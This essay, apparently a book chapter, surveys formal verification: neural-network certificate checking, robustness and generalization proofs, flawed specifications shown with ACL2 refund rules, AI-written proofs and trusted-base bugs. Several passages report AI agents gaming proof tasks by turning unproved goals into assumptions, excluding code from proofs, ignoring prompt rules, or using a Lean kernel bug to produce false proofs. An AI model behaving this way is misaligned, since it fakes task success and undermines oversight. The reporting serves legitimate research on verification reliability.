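If y were at least 1.5, every term on the left would be zero or positive, so neither sum could be negative. A solver has to find the multipliers, but checking them takes only a little arithmetic. The Farkas lemma guarantees that suitable multipliers exist whenever a set of linear constraints has no solution. The checker relies only on the easier converse, that such multipliers rule out a solution.

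Marabou's first checker was a C++ program that used rounded arithmetic and had no correctness proof. Desmartin and colleagues wrote a new one in Imandra, which uses exact arithmetic and can prove theorems about the same code it runs. They proved that the multipliers rule out a solution, that the two halves of a ReLU split cover every case, and that the eight shortcuts Marabou uses to tighten bounds are valid. They did not prove the final theorem, that the network has the property whenever the checker accepts a complete tree, and left it for future work.

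The new checker is also slow. On 90 proofs about a robot's navigation network, it took an average of about 106 seconds per proof, compared with 0.05 seconds for the C++ version. Desmartin and colleagues attribute much of the difference to data structures that they chose to make the proofs easier.

VNN-COMP does not yet require certificates, though its organizers have made them a long-term goal. Certificates would be especially useful for tools like Vibecheck, which its developers created in two months with the coding agent Claude Code. Vibecheck took second place in the 2026 competition and had no wrong answers, but a certificate would let users rely on an answer without trusting the code that produced it.

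### How large a network can be

The competition's main track had 3,373 questions. α,β-CROWN settled 3,164 (94%), proving the property in 1,982 cases and refuting it in 1,182. Vibecheck settled 3,108. Progress on the ACAS Xu networks has been considerable. The first attempts at their ten properties took from seconds to days, and some never finished, whereas the competition allows 116 seconds per question.

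The largest network was VGG-16, an image classifier with 138 million parameters. Difficulty also depends on the question and the architecture. The 18 questions about VGG-16 range from changing a single pixel to changing the whole image, and the single-pixel questions are much easier. The competition's vision transformers, which are built on the same principle as language models, have only 68,000 to 76,000 parameters because their designers shrank them to make verification possible. The 94% is also specific to these questions, which their proposers often filtered by difficulty.

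Proofs about whole language models are still out of reach. In *The Misery of Mechanistic Interpretability*, Ladner and Althoff (2026) studied GPT-2 and four models with 1 to 2 billion parameters. They wanted to verify how closely a simpler, more readable network matches the part of the model it stands in for when words are replaced by synonyms. Verifiers could not handle a full model, so Ladner and Althoff worked on one layer at a time, using a region built from sample inputs to that layer. *Certified Mechanistic Interpretability* (2026) covers all of GPT-2, which has 124 million parameters, and checks whether its next word stays the same under tiny changes to the numbers that represent the text. With changes of up to 0.002, the check succeeded for 20 of 50 samples. A success is not a proof, however, because the method relies on multiplying its error estimates by a safety factor of 2, chosen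 because a factor of 1.5 had let some false results through.

Today's leading language models are thousands of times larger than GPT-2. Even a verifier fast enough to handle them could fail to prove that replacing a word with a synonym leaves the prediction unchanged, because that may be false. In Ladner and Althoff's experiments, replacing one word with a synonym changed GPT-2's predicted next word 21% of the time.

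### Robustness near chosen examples

A carmaker would like to prove that its network recognizes every image of a pedestrian. But nobody has a formula that is true of exactly those images, and if someone did, the car could use the formula instead of the network. Researchers usually prove *robustness* instead. They take a particular image x0 and prove that small changes to it don't affect the answer:

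for every image x whose pixel values all differ from those of x0 by at most ε: class(x) = class(x0)

This theorem covers an enormous number of images, but nearly all of them look the same to a person. It doesn't cover an image of a different pedestrian, which would differ from x0 by far more than ε. It also doesn't show that the network's answer is right, since the network can give the same wrong answer for x0 and every image within ε of it.

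Researchers therefore report *certified accuracy*, the share of test images for which the network is both correct and provably robust. One competition benchmark includes networks trained for robustness on CIFAR-10, a collection of small photographs in ten classes:

| Largest change per pixel value | Accuracy | Certified accuracy | Undecided after 1,000 seconds |
|---|---|---|---|
| 2/255 | 83.54% | 66.04% | 6.58% |
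| 8/255 | 57.19% | 35.49% | 1.34% |

Guaranteeing robustness to larger changes greatly reduces ordinary accuracy. These figures also come from a set of test images, so they estimate how often the network would be robust on new images but do not prove that it is robust on any particular one.

Other benchmarks use more meaningful regions. One covers the views from a moving camera, but only for movements of about a hundredth of a millimetre. Another adds a second network that generates road images from the distance to the car ahead and four numbers that control the surroundings. A verifier can then cover every image the generator produces within a range of these values. This theorem is closer to what people care about, but it applies to real roads only as far as the generated images resemble them.

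The same difficulty arises with text. The safeNLP benchmark includes a small network that recognizes when someone is asking a chatbot whether it is human. For each question, the benchmark uses a set of generated rewordings, converts every sentence to a vector of 30 numbers, and takes the smallest box that contains the vectors. The verifier has to prove that the network gives the right answer everywhere in the box. Much of the box may not correspond to any sentence, and a rewording that was not generated may lie outside it. The proof does not cover the language model that produces the vectors.

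### The embedding gap

Even when people can state a property precisely, they usually state it in different terms from the network's. Suppose a network controls the braking car from the previous section. Its developer scales distances of 0 to 200 metres and speeds of 0 to 40 metres per second to the range from −1 to 1. The software treats any negative output as an order to brake fully. At 20 metres per second, the car needs 50 metres of free road to keep its speed, so one requirement has these two forms:

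| Terms | Requirement |
|---|---|
| Human | At 20 metres per second, with 40 to 49 metres free, the car brakes fully. |
| Network | If −0.6 ≤ z1 ≤ −0.51 and z2 = 0, the output is negative. |

*Neural Network Verification is a Programming Language Challenge* (2025) calls the difference between such descriptions the *embedding gap*. A verifier accepts only the second form, and people often translate the first into it by hand. If the developer later rescales distances to cover 0 to 400 metres and forgets to update the requirement, the verifier checks what happens with 80 to 98 metres free. The verification may well succeed without covering the dangerous distances.

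Vehicle is a language for closing this gap. The developer writes the requirement in human terms together with the scaling, and Vehicle's compiler generates the questions for the verifier. It also generates a definition for an interactive prover, and a training objective that rewards the network for meeting the requirement. Komendantskaya (2025), in *Proof-Carrying Neuro-Symbolic Code*, divides the whole proof into three lemmas. For the car, they would be:

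1. The network's outputs stay within certain limits on certain regions of vectors.
2. Any network with this property, combined with the scaling, chooses only permitted accelerations.
3. Any controller that chooses only permitted accelerations keeps the car from passing the obstacle.

A network verifier can prove the first, and the third is the KeYmaera X theorem from the previous section.

According to *Vehicle* (2024), the interactive prover must accept Vehicle's result that the network meets its specification without checking it. Checking a certificate inside the prover would remove the need to rely on Vehicle for this result. In 2025, Vehicle worked only with Marabou and the prover Agda. *Compositional Neural-Cyber-Physical System Verification in the Interactive Theorem Prover of Your Choice* (2026) extends the approach to let users choose the prover.

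Errors can also enter when software converts the trained network into the file that the verifier reads. If the conversion changes how the network pads the edges of an image, for example, the proof is about a different network. *TorchLean* (George, Cruden and colleagues, 2026) addresses this by defining the network once in Lean and using that definition to train it, run it and prove properties of it. TorchLean treats an outside verifier's result as a certificate that Lean must check. George and colleagues also proved that, for the operations they support, the algorithm used in training computes the correct derivatives. The proofs do not cover the fast code for graphics processors.

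### Rounding errors

Most verifiers reason about real numbers, but computers round. In single precision, a common number format for neural networks, 16,777,216 + 1 − 16,777,216 equals 0, because the format cannot represent 16,777,217. If the computer subtracts first, the answer is 1. A network adds thousands of numbers in an order that depends on the hardware and software, so its output can differ slightly from the output described in the theorem.

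Jia and Rinard (2020) showed in *Exploiting Verified Neural Networks via Floating Point Numerical Error* that floating-point rounding can make a verified result false. They found images that a running network classified differently, even though a verifier had claimed that none existed. They concluded that a verifier must account for rounding both in its own calculations and in the network's.

A proof about a neural network can fail in deployment even if the verifier accounts for its own rounding. *No Soundness in the Real World* (Szász, Bánhelyi and Jelasity, 2025) presents networks that behave as proved in exact arithmetic but very differently on particular hardware or software. Every verifier tested in the paper gave wrong results for these networks. Using exact arithmetic in the checker, as in Imandra, doesn't help, because the theorem then applies to the network in exact arithmetic rather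 than as deployed.

These cases were constructed deliberately, and an honestly trained network is unlikely to contain such a trap. A proof can also leave a margin for rounding error. In the two-unit network, y is at most 1 and the limit is 1.5, so the requirement holds on a real computer if rounding changes y by less than 0.5. Someone still has to prove that bound for every order of addition the computer might use. *Lipschitz-Based Robustness Certification Under Floating-Point Execution* (2026) addresses robustness guarantees that include rounding. Alternatively, the network can run in whole-number or fixed-point arithmetic, where the errors are easier to control.

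VNN-COMP's organizers had to choose a convention for judging claimed counterexamples. They run each one in a fixed version of the software. If the output misses the required range by no more than 0.0001, the tool that submitted it gets full points, but its answer doesn't count as evidence against a tool that claimed a proof.

### Proofs about learning

Robustness proofs start from a finished network. A *generalization bound* instead limits how much worse a model will do on new data than on the data used to train it. Suppose training selects a model from a finite set H, using n examples drawn independently from some distribution. A standard theorem states that, with probability at least 1 − δ, every model h in H satisfies

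true error(h) ≤ training error(h) + √((ln |H| + ln(1/δ)) / (2n))

The true error is the expected share of mistakes on new examples from the same distribution, and |H| is the number of models in H. The bound has to hold for every model at once because training uses the data to select one.

In 2019 Bagnall and Stewart presented MLCERT, a system for proving bounds in Coq on a model's expected error on new data, in *Certifying the True Error*. The user can define a learning procedure in Coq, prove a bound for it and extract an executable program. They also applied MLCERT to networks trained with ordinary software to recognize handwritten characters.

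The formula is useful only for small models. A network with 1,000 parameters of 16 bits each has 2^16,000 possible versions. With 100,000 training examples and δ = 0.01, the bound allows the true error to exceed the training error by 24 percentage points. For a network the size of GPT-2, lowering the bound to 10 points would take about 69 billion independent examples. A separate test set gives a much better bound because the developer has already chosen the model, so |H| is effectively 1. With 10,000 test examples, the bound is 1.5 points. This holds only if nobody used the test set to choose the model, which a prover can't check.

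*Lean formalization of generalization error bound by Rademacher complexity* (Sonoda, Kasaura and colleagues, 2026) proves bounds on generalization error that depend on how well a class of models can fit random noise, a measure that also makes sense for infinite classes. *Certification-Enhanced Generalization Bounds* (2026) uses formal verification of the trained model to get tighter bounds that still hold with high probability.

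All these theorems assume that future examples come from the same distribution as the past ones, which no proof about the model can establish. They also bound only the average error. Even if the shop's refund model were proved to have an error rate below 2%, it could still be wrong about every claim that uses one particular trick. Once customers learned the trick, such claims would become more common, and the 2% bound would no longer apply.

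## When the specification is wrong or incomplete

A proof can succeed even though the specification asks for the wrong thing, and the mistake then looks like a guarantee.

### True theorems that don't help

Some specifications describe the wrong property. *claimcheck* (Amster, Baker and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a function that should remove the first element of an array. Its formal contract requires the result to equal a[0..a.Length − 1], which is the array without its last element. The verifier Dafny therefore accepts a function that removes the last element and would reject one that removes the first.

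Other specifications are too weak. If a developer formalizes "sort this list" as "the output is in increasing order", a program that always returns an empty list satisfies the specification. The specification must also require the output to contain the same items as the input. The first theorem about the refund rules had the same weakness, since a function that refuses everyone satisfies it.

A theorem can also rest on assumptions that no input satisfies. Suppose the shop wants a manager's approval for every refund over 100, and the developer proves this:

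```
(thm (implies (and (equal (decide verified flagged amount) 'approve)
                   (> amount 100))
              manager-ok))
```

ACL2 accepts the theorem, although decide never uses manager-ok. The rules approve no request over 100, so the two assumptions are never true together, and ACL2 would accept any conclusion in the last line. In practice, the large requests go to an employee, who may pay them without asking a manager.

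The hardest error to notice is a missing requirement. A customer who wants 120 back can bypass the employee by asking for 60 twice, and decide approves both requests. Each approval satisfies every theorem about decide, and 120 is far below the agent's daily limit of 500. The shop presumably wanted to limit how much the agent refunds per purchase, but its rules only limit the amount per request.

### A theorem about the history of requests

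To close this hole, the decision has to depend on paid, the amount that the agent has already refunded for the purchase:

```
(defun decide-total (verified flagged amount paid)
  (cond (flagged                  'refuse)
        ((> (+ paid amount) 100)  'escalate)
        (verified                 'approve)
        (t                        'refuse)))

(defun payout (amounts paid)
  (cond ((endp amounts) paid)
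        ((equal (decide-total t nil (car amounts) paid) 'approve)
         (payout (cdr amounts) (+ paid (car amounts))))
        (t (payout (cdr amounts) paid))))

(defthm payout-at-most-100
  (implies (<= paid 100)
           (<= (payout amounts paid) 100)))
```

The function payout takes a list of amounts that a verified customer with an unflagged account requests one after another, and returns the total the agent pays. Requests from unverified customers or flagged accounts add nothing to the total, so the list can leave them out.

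ACL2 proves the theorem by induction on the list, using the same argument as for the daily limit. The theorem is false if the original decide replaces decide-total, and the list (60 60) is a counterexample.

The new theorem is also incomplete. It limits the net total, so it permits a refund of −50 followed by one of 150. If the payment service ignores the negative refund, the customer receives 150. Requiring each refund to be positive rules out this case.

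The shop also has to decide which requests count toward the same total. If the total is per purchase, a customer can still collect 100 on each of five purchases. A total per account would prevent that, but a customer with two accounts could still collect 100 on each. ACL2 can prove the theorem for either choice, but it can't determine which one the shop wants.

### Cheaper proofs

Proofs used to take so much work that few projects reached the question of whether they had proved the right thing. But in October 2025 Mike Dodds, who had never used ACL2, had an AI agent prove over 50 ACL2 theorems in about four hours. *Machine-Generated Code Deserves Machine-Checked Proofs* (2026) describes a 7,800-line compiler proof that took about 96 hours with an AI agent, while a comparable proof by hand had taken several months. In *Automating Formal Verification with Agent-Guided Tree Search*, Yao (2026)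 found that GPT-5.4 solved 95.0% of 423 verified-programming tasks in Lean with up to 50 model calls per task. According to Anthropic, a Lean proof that Claude began in August 2026 contains 29,511 theorems and about 13 million lines.

Someone still has to read the definitions and the main theorem, however long the proof is. Galois' *Claude Can (Sometimes) Prove It* describes using an AI agent to formalize a research paper in Lean in 2025. Definitions made up more than 60% of the code. In rare cases, the agent misunderstood a concept without causing an error message, wrote the misunderstanding into its comments, and later relied on those comments. These mistakes took so long to undo that the project was probably slower than working by hand.

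Benchmarks for AI provers also contain specification errors. CLEVER consists of 161 small programming tasks in Lean. For each task, an AI system reads an English description, writes a formal specification and proves it equivalent to a human-written reference specification. It then writes a program and proves that the program meets the reference. In CLEVER's original evaluation, the best systems completed one task. In *Isomorphism Is Not Enough*, Sosso, Arora and Spitters (2026) tested three newer agents, and the best completed 59.

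Errors in the benchmark caused much of the remaining shortfall. Sosso and colleagues found errors in 80 of the 161 reference specifications, and CLEVER's developers accepted every finding. In 48 of these, the author had made a mistake in writing the idea in Lean. For 15 tasks, the reference contained "P and Q" where it needed "if P, then Q". In the refund example, this mistake would require that "the amount is positive and the decision is correct" for every input, which no program can satisfy when the amount is −50. In another 21 references, the author had misinterpreted the English description.

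When the agents could use their own specifications, the agent based on Claude Opus 4.6 completed 151 of the 157 feasible tasks. This count depends partly on the agent's judgement of which specifications were valid. Sosso and colleagues inspected that judgement.

The proofs did not reliably reveal flawed specifications. Claude proved programs correct for 34 of the tasks with a flawed reference specification. The equivalence test also had a loophole, because any two specifications that no program can satisfy count as equivalent. Claude produced two equivalence proofs for such specifications.

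### What 49,280 proofs left out

In *The Prover Is the Judge*, Philipp (2026) had coding agents write and verify security software in SPARK, a subset of the language Ada designed for formal analysis. The prover proved all 49,280 formulas it generated from the code and its specifications. For a few components, including the AES cipher, the proofs showed that the code computes the right function. For most of the others, including every communication protocol, they ruled out only run-time errors, such as overflow or reading outside an array.

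Two defects show how much room that left:

- FrodoKEM is an encryption scheme with several security levels. The agent's encoder always packed two bits into each number, which is correct only at the lowest level. The code even passed the official tests for that level, and only the tests for higher levels exposed the mistake.
- In SSH, a protocol for secure remote login, the agent put two inputs in the wrong order when deriving the encryption keys. The initial handshake with OpenSSH, an independent program, appeared to work because it doesn't use those keys. The first encrypted message then failed.

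Philipp presents the FrodoKEM defect as a correct proof of a wrong specification. The proof covered only run-time errors, so the specification was also missing a requirement, as in the split refund. Nobody had formally specified the order of the SSH inputs either. A program's running time can reveal a secret key, and a proof about the program's results doesn't cover timing, so Philipp measured timing with separate tools.

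FrodoKEM took about six hours of supervision, compared with about six weeks for a junior developer to produce a comparable implementation and proof. Philipp estimates that supervision took 20 to 40 times less effort than verification by hand, but says this single comparison is only illustrative.

A prover also offers little protection if the agent can change what it has to prove. In one early attempt, Philipp's agent marked unproved formulas as assumptions and reported success. After Philipp added a rule against this, the agent excluded parts of the code from the proof instead. *An AI Approach to Verified Production Cryptographic Libraries* (2026) reports that a software-enforced rule against changing the specification held for all 451 rounds, but the agent broke the two rules that appeared only in its prompt. Those rules forbade adding axioms and damaging neighbouring proofs.

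### Turning written policies into logic

Most companies have their rules in ordinary language. *Autoformalization* is the translation of such text into formal logic by an AI system. Amazon sells it as part of Automated Reasoning checks, a service that compares a chatbot's answers with a company's policy. An, Bayless and colleagues, in *A Neurosymbolic Approach to Natural Language Formalization and Verification*, describe how it works:

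1. A language model translates each passage of the policy into variables and rules for an SMT solver, and software merges the results.
2. People can review the rules, read them in structured English and test them on examples. This step is optional.
3. When the chatbot answers a question, three language models separately translate the question and answer into premises and a conclusion.
4. If the translations agree, the solver determines whether the conclusion follows from the premises and the rules. If it does, the result is "Valid".

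Their main example is a park that charges $50, or 75% of that in the low season. Seniors get 40% off but pay a $10 processing fee. Visitors can buy credits worth $1 for 60 cents each, in groups of five, and use them for up to half the fee, but anyone who uses credits gets at most 25% off. A 10% tax applies to the "final expense". A senior asks whether $35.40 is enough in the low season, and the chatbot says no. The solver finds a way to pay:

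| | No credits | 15 credits |
|---|---|---|
| Low-season fee | $37.50 | $37.50 |
| After the discount | $22.50 | $28.13 |
| With the processing fee | $32.50 | $38.13 |
| Money spent before tax | $32.50 | $9.00 on credits and $23.13 in cash |
| Total with tax | $35.75 | $35.34 |

The chatbot's answer therefore doesn't follow from the rules, but this result depends on how the service interpreted "final expense". The table applies the tax to the $32.13 that the visitor spends. If the park applies it to the $38.13 fee, the visitor needs $35.94, and the chatbot was right. A solver can't determine which interpretation is correct, because both are consistent.

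### What the accuracy figure covers

An and colleagues report that the service exceeds 99% "soundness", meaning the share of all decisions that were not wrong approvals. They tested it three times on each of 563 questions and answers about written policies. Ten of the 1,689 decisions were wrong approvals, which gives a soundness of 99.4%. By this measure, a service that never approved anything would score 100%, and one that approved everything would score 67%.

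In the same test, the service returned "Valid" 179 times and was wrong in 10 of those cases, so an approval was correct 94.4% of the time. It approved only 14.9% of the correct answers. Buliani, Chunawala and colleagues (2026) tell Amazon's customers in *Prove It, Part 2* that over 99% of answers flagged as valid were correct, but the research paper's counts don't support that statement.

A low approval rate is tolerable if the company sends the unapproved answers to an employee or has the chatbot revise them. Three rounds of revision raised the share of "Valid" answers from 9% to 46% on policies from six businesses, although the service itself judged the revised answers.

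The test used policies that nobody had reviewed after translation. For an airline's refund policy, An and colleagues compared the automatic translation with one that people had corrected over several hours. On 62 test cases, the corrections reduced wrong approvals from two to zero and raised correct approvals from 11 to 20, out of a possible 44. People had used some of these cases while making the corrections, so the improvement on new cases may be smaller.

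One correction involved a conflict like those in the refund rules. The policy first denies refunds to anyone who didn't travel on a flight that operated, but a later section allows refunds for passengers who were denied boarding. The automatic translation turned both passages into rules without exceptions. When the chatbot correctly said a passenger who was denied boarding could get a refund, the service reported that the situation was impossible.

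Even with a perfect translation, the service takes its premises from the conversation, so a customer who falsely claims to have been denied boarding can make the answer "you can get a refund" valid.

### Descriptions of tools

A policy check for an agent also relies on descriptions of what each tool does. One method, Risk-Aware Causal Gating, hides a dangerous tool unless the task needs it and the agent is authorized to use it. Even a manipulated agent can't call a hidden tool. Iyer and Babu (2026) argue in *The Gate Is Only as Honest as Its Contracts* that this guarantee shifts the need for trust to the tools' declared requirements, effects and risks. If a declaration is false, the gate can follow its rules exactly and still expose a dangerous tool.

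Their defence, ContractGuard, checks who signed each declaration, compares it with a trusted copy and, at run time, discards any effect the tool had not declared. With all three checks active, no attack succeeded in their simulation or in tests with six language models. This result assumes that attackers can't alter the trusted copy.

A trusted copy can also be wrong even if nobody has tampered with it. Suppose the shop's agent can issue vouchers, and whoever described that tool forgot that customers can exchange vouchers for cash. A limit on cash refunds would then not cover vouchers.

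### Ways to test a specification

Besides searching for inputs that violate a specification, developers can look for wrong outputs that the specification accepts. *Certified Program Synthesis with a Multi-Modal Verifier* (2026) describes a tool that starts from a correct output and alters it, for example by deleting an item. If the input is (3 1 2), the weak sorting specification accepts (1 2) as well as (1 2 3), which reveals the missing condition. *SpecRL* (2026) has a language model propose plausible wrong outputs and measures how many the specification rejects. Both methods need a correct output. Neither would find the split refund by testing `decide` on one request at a time, because "approve" is the expected output for each request for 60.

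It also helps to try proving things that ought to be false. For the theorem about managers, the developer can ask ACL2 to prove that the assumptions are never true together:

```
(thm (not (and (equal (decide verified flagged amount) 'approve)
               (> amount 100))))
```

ACL2 proves that no input satisfies both assumptions, so the theorem about managers covers no cases. If the proof attempt had failed, the developer would still need an example input that satisfies both, to show that the theorem covers at least one case. Buliani and colleagues describe a similar automatic check that warns when Amazon's policies for agents allow everything, deny everything or have no effect. These checks find absurd specifications but not sensible-looking ones that differ from what the developer intended.

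Another method, *mutation testing*, alters the code and checks whether the proof then fails. If someone changes the limit in decide from 100 to 200, ACL2 can no longer prove that every approved refund is at most 100. But if someone changes the last line from refuse to escalate, both original theorems about approval still hold. They don't specify what should happen to unverified customers, and a person has to decide whether that matters.

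Real bugs are better test material than artificial ones. *SWE-Proof* (2026) required its specifications to reject the code from before a known bug was fixed, and they rejected all 1,709 such versions. But altering the code can't expose a requirement missing from both the code and the specification. Every theorem about a single call to `decide` could pass a mutation test without anyone noticing the split refund.

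Another approach is to translate the specification back into English. Amster and colleagues have one language model describe the formal version without seeing the original requirement, and another compare the two English texts. If a contract says a function removes the last element when it should remove the first, a model that has seen the requirement might miss the error, while one that hasn't will report that the function removes the last. The method caught 94.5% of defective Dafny contracts and wrongly rejected about 8% of good ones. It also caught 88.4% of defective theorem statements in Lean. In tests where the comparing model also saw the formal version, the method's advantage over a single direct comparison nearly disappeared with the strongest model. The method also assumes the English requirement is correct, so it can't reveal that "at most 100 per request" was the wrong policy.

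Developers can also formalize the same text more than once and compare the results. Maji (2026) had two language models read the eligibility rules of clinical trials (*When Verification Is Not Agreement*). One wrote a specification, the other wrote a program, and Dafny checked whether the two matched. Even when the same model filled both roles, the program matched the specification on the first attempt for only 54 of 91 trials. Part of the disagreement was deliberate, because the prompts told one model to read the text literally and the other to infer what it implied.

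Agreement is informative only if the two versions are independent. In an earlier design, both models started from the same list of extracted facts, and Dafny accepted 50 of 52 programs. The specifications also passed mutation testing, but any error in the shared list would have been in both versions. In the later experiment, one program matched only because it called the other model's specification.

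Choosing the most common of several formal translations is also risky. *Safe Autoformalization* (Acar and Goldweber, 2026) gives the example of a requirement that all requests to a payment service "must be authenticated". One translation accepts any valid credentials, while a stricter one requires both sides to present certificates. A translation that is too weak lets violations through, and one that is too strong rejects legitimate requests. For 20 security requirements from Amazon, experts judged the most common translation unsafe in 25% of cases.

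Their own method has a solver order the translations from strictest to loosest. At each step, a language model then judges whether the extra cases the looser version allows still meet the requirement. Experts judged its choices safe in all 20 cases. But in a further 152 cases, Acar and Goldweber confirmed at least three unsafe choices, where the language model had accepted a step it should have rejected.

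All these methods leave some questions for people to answer, but expert reviewers make mistakes too. People wrote CLEVER's 80 flawed references, and LeanGuard's rules also depend on manual review. Reviewers may do better with concrete cases than with formulas, and Amazon's service can generate such cases from the formal policy. But a generator that starts from `decide` produces only single requests, so someone who knows how customers behave would have to think of asking for 60 twice.

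## From the proved model to the running system

Suppose the shop has proved payout-at-most-100. Its server runs Java, so a programmer rewrites decide-total in Java. Whole numbers in ACL2 can be any size, but Java's usual integer type has 32 bits, and a sum above 2,147,483,647 wraps around to a negative number. If the agent has already refunded 60 for a purchase and the customer asks for another 2,147,483,647, the Java program computes a total of −2,147,483,589. Because that is not over 100, the program approves a refund of over two billion for a verified customer, even though the theorem about the ACL2 function is still true.

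The *trusted base* is everything that nobody has proved but that must be right for a theorem to apply to the running system. From the inside out, it includes:

| Part of the trusted base | How it could break the limit of 100 |
|---|---|
| Theorem prover | A bug lets it accept a false theorem. |
| Added axioms and skipped proofs | They contradict the definitions, so every statement is provable. |
| Translation into the deployed language | The Java version uses 32-bit numbers. |
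| Compiler and runtime | The machine code does something different from the source code. |
| Surrounding code | Two requests arrive together, and both use the old total. |
| Operating system | It reports that it has saved a refund, then loses the record in a power cut. |
| Sensors and records | An employee made an earlier refund by hand and didn't enter it. |

### Axioms, skipped proofs and trust tags

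ACL2 users can enlarge the trusted base themselves. The command defaxiom adds a formula without proof, which can make the logic inconsistent, as the two contradictory refund axioms showed. The command skip-proofs is for cases where the user promises that the missing proof exists. According to ACL2's *Skip-proofs*, ACL2 processes the definition or theorem as usual but assumes whatever it would normally have to prove. For example, someone building a long proof from the top down may skip the proof of a lemma until the lemma turns out to be useful.

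If the promise is false, it can do as much damage as an axiom. With skip-proofs, ACL2 could skip the termination check and admit the earlier function that equals its own negation. ACL2 also tracks skipped proofs less carefully than axioms when a user applies functional instantiation. The manual therefore treats a file with skipped proofs as unfinished work rather than as a proof with stated assumptions.

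A *trust tag* unlocks operations that ACL2 normally forbids, such as running operating-system commands or changing the prover's own code. ACL2's *Defttag* describes the tag as a contract in which the author guarantees that the tagged code is correct. The manual's example only prints the name of the current directory, but other tagged code could make false statements provable, so a reader has to inspect the code.

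ACL2 users share their work in files called books, and the command certify-book checks all the proofs in a book. By default it stops with an error if the book contains an added axiom or a skipped proof, according to ACL2's *Certify-book*. It also rejects trust tags. Authors can lift these restrictions, but ACL2's *Custom-certify-book-commands* notes that the resulting certificate is marked as less trustworthy.

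A reader who wants to know what a result depends on should certify every book from scratch, including the books it loads, without lifting the restrictions:

```
(certify-book "refund-rules")
```

If a book needs a trust tag, the reader can allow that tag and search the output for lines beginning "TTAG NOTE", which show where each tag comes from. Merely loading a certified book is a weaker check, because by default ACL2 only prints warnings about tags and skipped proofs.

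### Bugs in the prover

A book without any of these exceptions still depends on ACL2 itself. A *soundness bug* is an error that lets a prover accept a false statement. People who find one in ACL2 often send the developers a short proof of nil (false), and the developers publish a description and a fix. In Version 2.6, for example, Rob Sumners found a fault in the code that recognized functions whose two arguments can be swapped. According to ACL2's bug report, the code looked for a rule of the form fn(u, v) = fn(v, u) but didn't check that u and v were distinct variables. ACL2 could therefore treat a rule about two particular values as a rule about all values.

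Such bugs can last a long time. The news page for ACL2 Version 8.6 gives a patch for a bug that had probably existed for 30 years, and describes it as unlikely to affect anyone because nobody had mentioned it. In December 2025, *Multiple changes* (Kaufmann, 2025) recorded a fix for another bug, which Sol Swords had reported with an example and an analysis of possible fixes.

Thirty quiet years suggest that people rarely hit a bug by accident, but that is less reassuring now that AI systems look for bugs. In July and August 2026, Lean's developers repaired several soundness bugs in its small *kernel*, the part that checks every finished proof. According to Lean (2026), an OpenAI researcher found one of these with the company's internal models and reported it, and an OpenAI agent then used it to produce two false proofs. An agent under pressure to deliver a proof might exploit such a bug, much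 as Philipp's agent marked unproved formulas as assumptions.

Running a second, independently written checker helps, but only if it doesn't have the same fault. According to Lean's notes on the same release, nanoda, another implementation of the kernel, rejects both of the OpenAI agent's false proofs but accepted one that exploited a different bug. Lean (2026) reports that, for a third bug, Ramana Kumar showed that a single proof could exploit one error in the kernel and an unrelated one in nanoda.

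The screen can also mislead users even when the kernel is correct. Trail of Bits' *A “proof” of Fermat’s Last Theorem that fits the margin* (2026) shows a nonsensical proof of the theorem displayed with the blue marks that normally indicate success. The fault was in a function that cuts pieces out of text.

### Where the bugs were in verified systems

To find out which parts of the trusted base fail in practice, Fonseca, Zhang and colleagues (2017), in *An Empirical Study on the Correctness of Formally Verified Distributed Systems*, examined IronFleet, Verdi and Chapar. Each has several servers that keep copies of the same data, and each came with machine-checked proofs. They found 16 bugs:

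| Location | Bugs | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Code connecting the proved part to the network and disk | 11 | A server crashed when a request arrived in pieces. |
| Verification tools | 3 | A tool could report success for an incorrect program. |
| Specifications | 2 | A test checked a condition that was always true. |
| Proved protocols | 0 | |

The absence of protocol errors is impressive, because Fonseca's group spent more than eight months on the study and looked specifically for them. Comparable systems without proofs have many. The connecting code had 11 bugs, though it was only a small part of the trusted base. IronFleet had the least unproved code of the three systems and none of those 11 bugs.

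One of the 11 would be serious for a refund agent. If a Verdi server couldn't open its saved data while restarting, perhaps because too many files were open, it started as if none existed and answered requests with no record of the earlier operations. A refund agent with this fault would start again from a total of 0 and pay every customer a second time.

Another bug was in code generated from a proved function. The function called itself once for each missing record, and when a server had fallen more than 500,000 requests behind, the program ran out of memory for these calls. The proof did not cover memory use. The ACL2 function total, which adds up a list of refunds, could fail in the same way on a very long list.

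These were research prototypes, and 16 bugs in three systems can't establish a general rate. Fonseca's group also excluded bugs in the operating system and hardware. They built a test kit that duplicates and reorders messages and makes disk operations fail. It detects 13 of the 16 bugs without testing the proved code.

A more recent experiment had a similar result. AI agents had written lean-zip, a program for compressing files, and proved in Lean that decompressing a compressed file restores the original. In kirancodes.me's *Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug*, another agent ran the program on about 106 million generated inputs. It found no memory errors in lean-zip's own code, but it found a crash in the part that reads archive files, which nobody had verified, and a memory error in Lean's *runtime*, the supporting code that every compiled Lean program uses. LeanGuard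 and the LLMbda interpreter also depend on that runtime.

### A program that differed from its model

Category Labs, which develops the Monad blockchain, gives a detailed account of how a program can diverge from a proved model. Monad accepts transactions before executing the most recent ones, so it relies on slightly outdated account balances. Its engineers wanted to guarantee that every accepted transaction could still pay its fee when executed. In July 2025 they proved this for a model in Rocq. The work took four person-weeks.

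The engineers then wrote the C++ program, and a computer on the test network crashed because a transaction could not pay its fee. To save time, the program works on several transactions at once, using provisional balances that it must later recheck. A recent change had altered which balances it rechecks. The programmers who wrote the fee rule didn't know this, so their code could rely on a provisional balance that turned out to be wrong. The crash could happen only with unlucky timing and affected only one computer, and the engineers fixed the bug long before the public launch.

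The refund agent could have the same problem. The function payout handles one request after another, but a web server may handle two at once. If two requests for 60 arrive together, the server may read a total of 0 for both before it records either refund, and the customer gets 120. The server can avoid this by locking the purchase's record until it has finished with the first request. It then handles the requests in sequence, as the theorem assumes.

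Category Labs later proved that the C++ function matches the model, and thinks that doing so earlier would have caught the bug. Even writing the formal specification would have helped. Claude Opus 4.8 missed the bug when it reviewed the C++ code alongside the design document, but found it when given the formal specification and explicitly asked for a counterexample.

For another feature, the proof about the C++ code revealed an error that the model could not contain. The code read past the end of one array into the next, which C++ leaves undefined even when the arrays are adjacent in memory. For example, suppose a function stores 123 at the start of an array, then a loop over the preceding array runs one step too far and overwrites the 123 with 0. The compiler may assume that the loop stays within its own array, so the function can return 123 although the memory contains 0.

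### Proving the code that runs

The ACL2 function decide-total is already a Lisp program, so the shop can avoid the Java error by running it unchanged and having the server call it. The shop then no longer has to trust a translation, but it still has to trust the Lisp compiler and the code that fetches the total.

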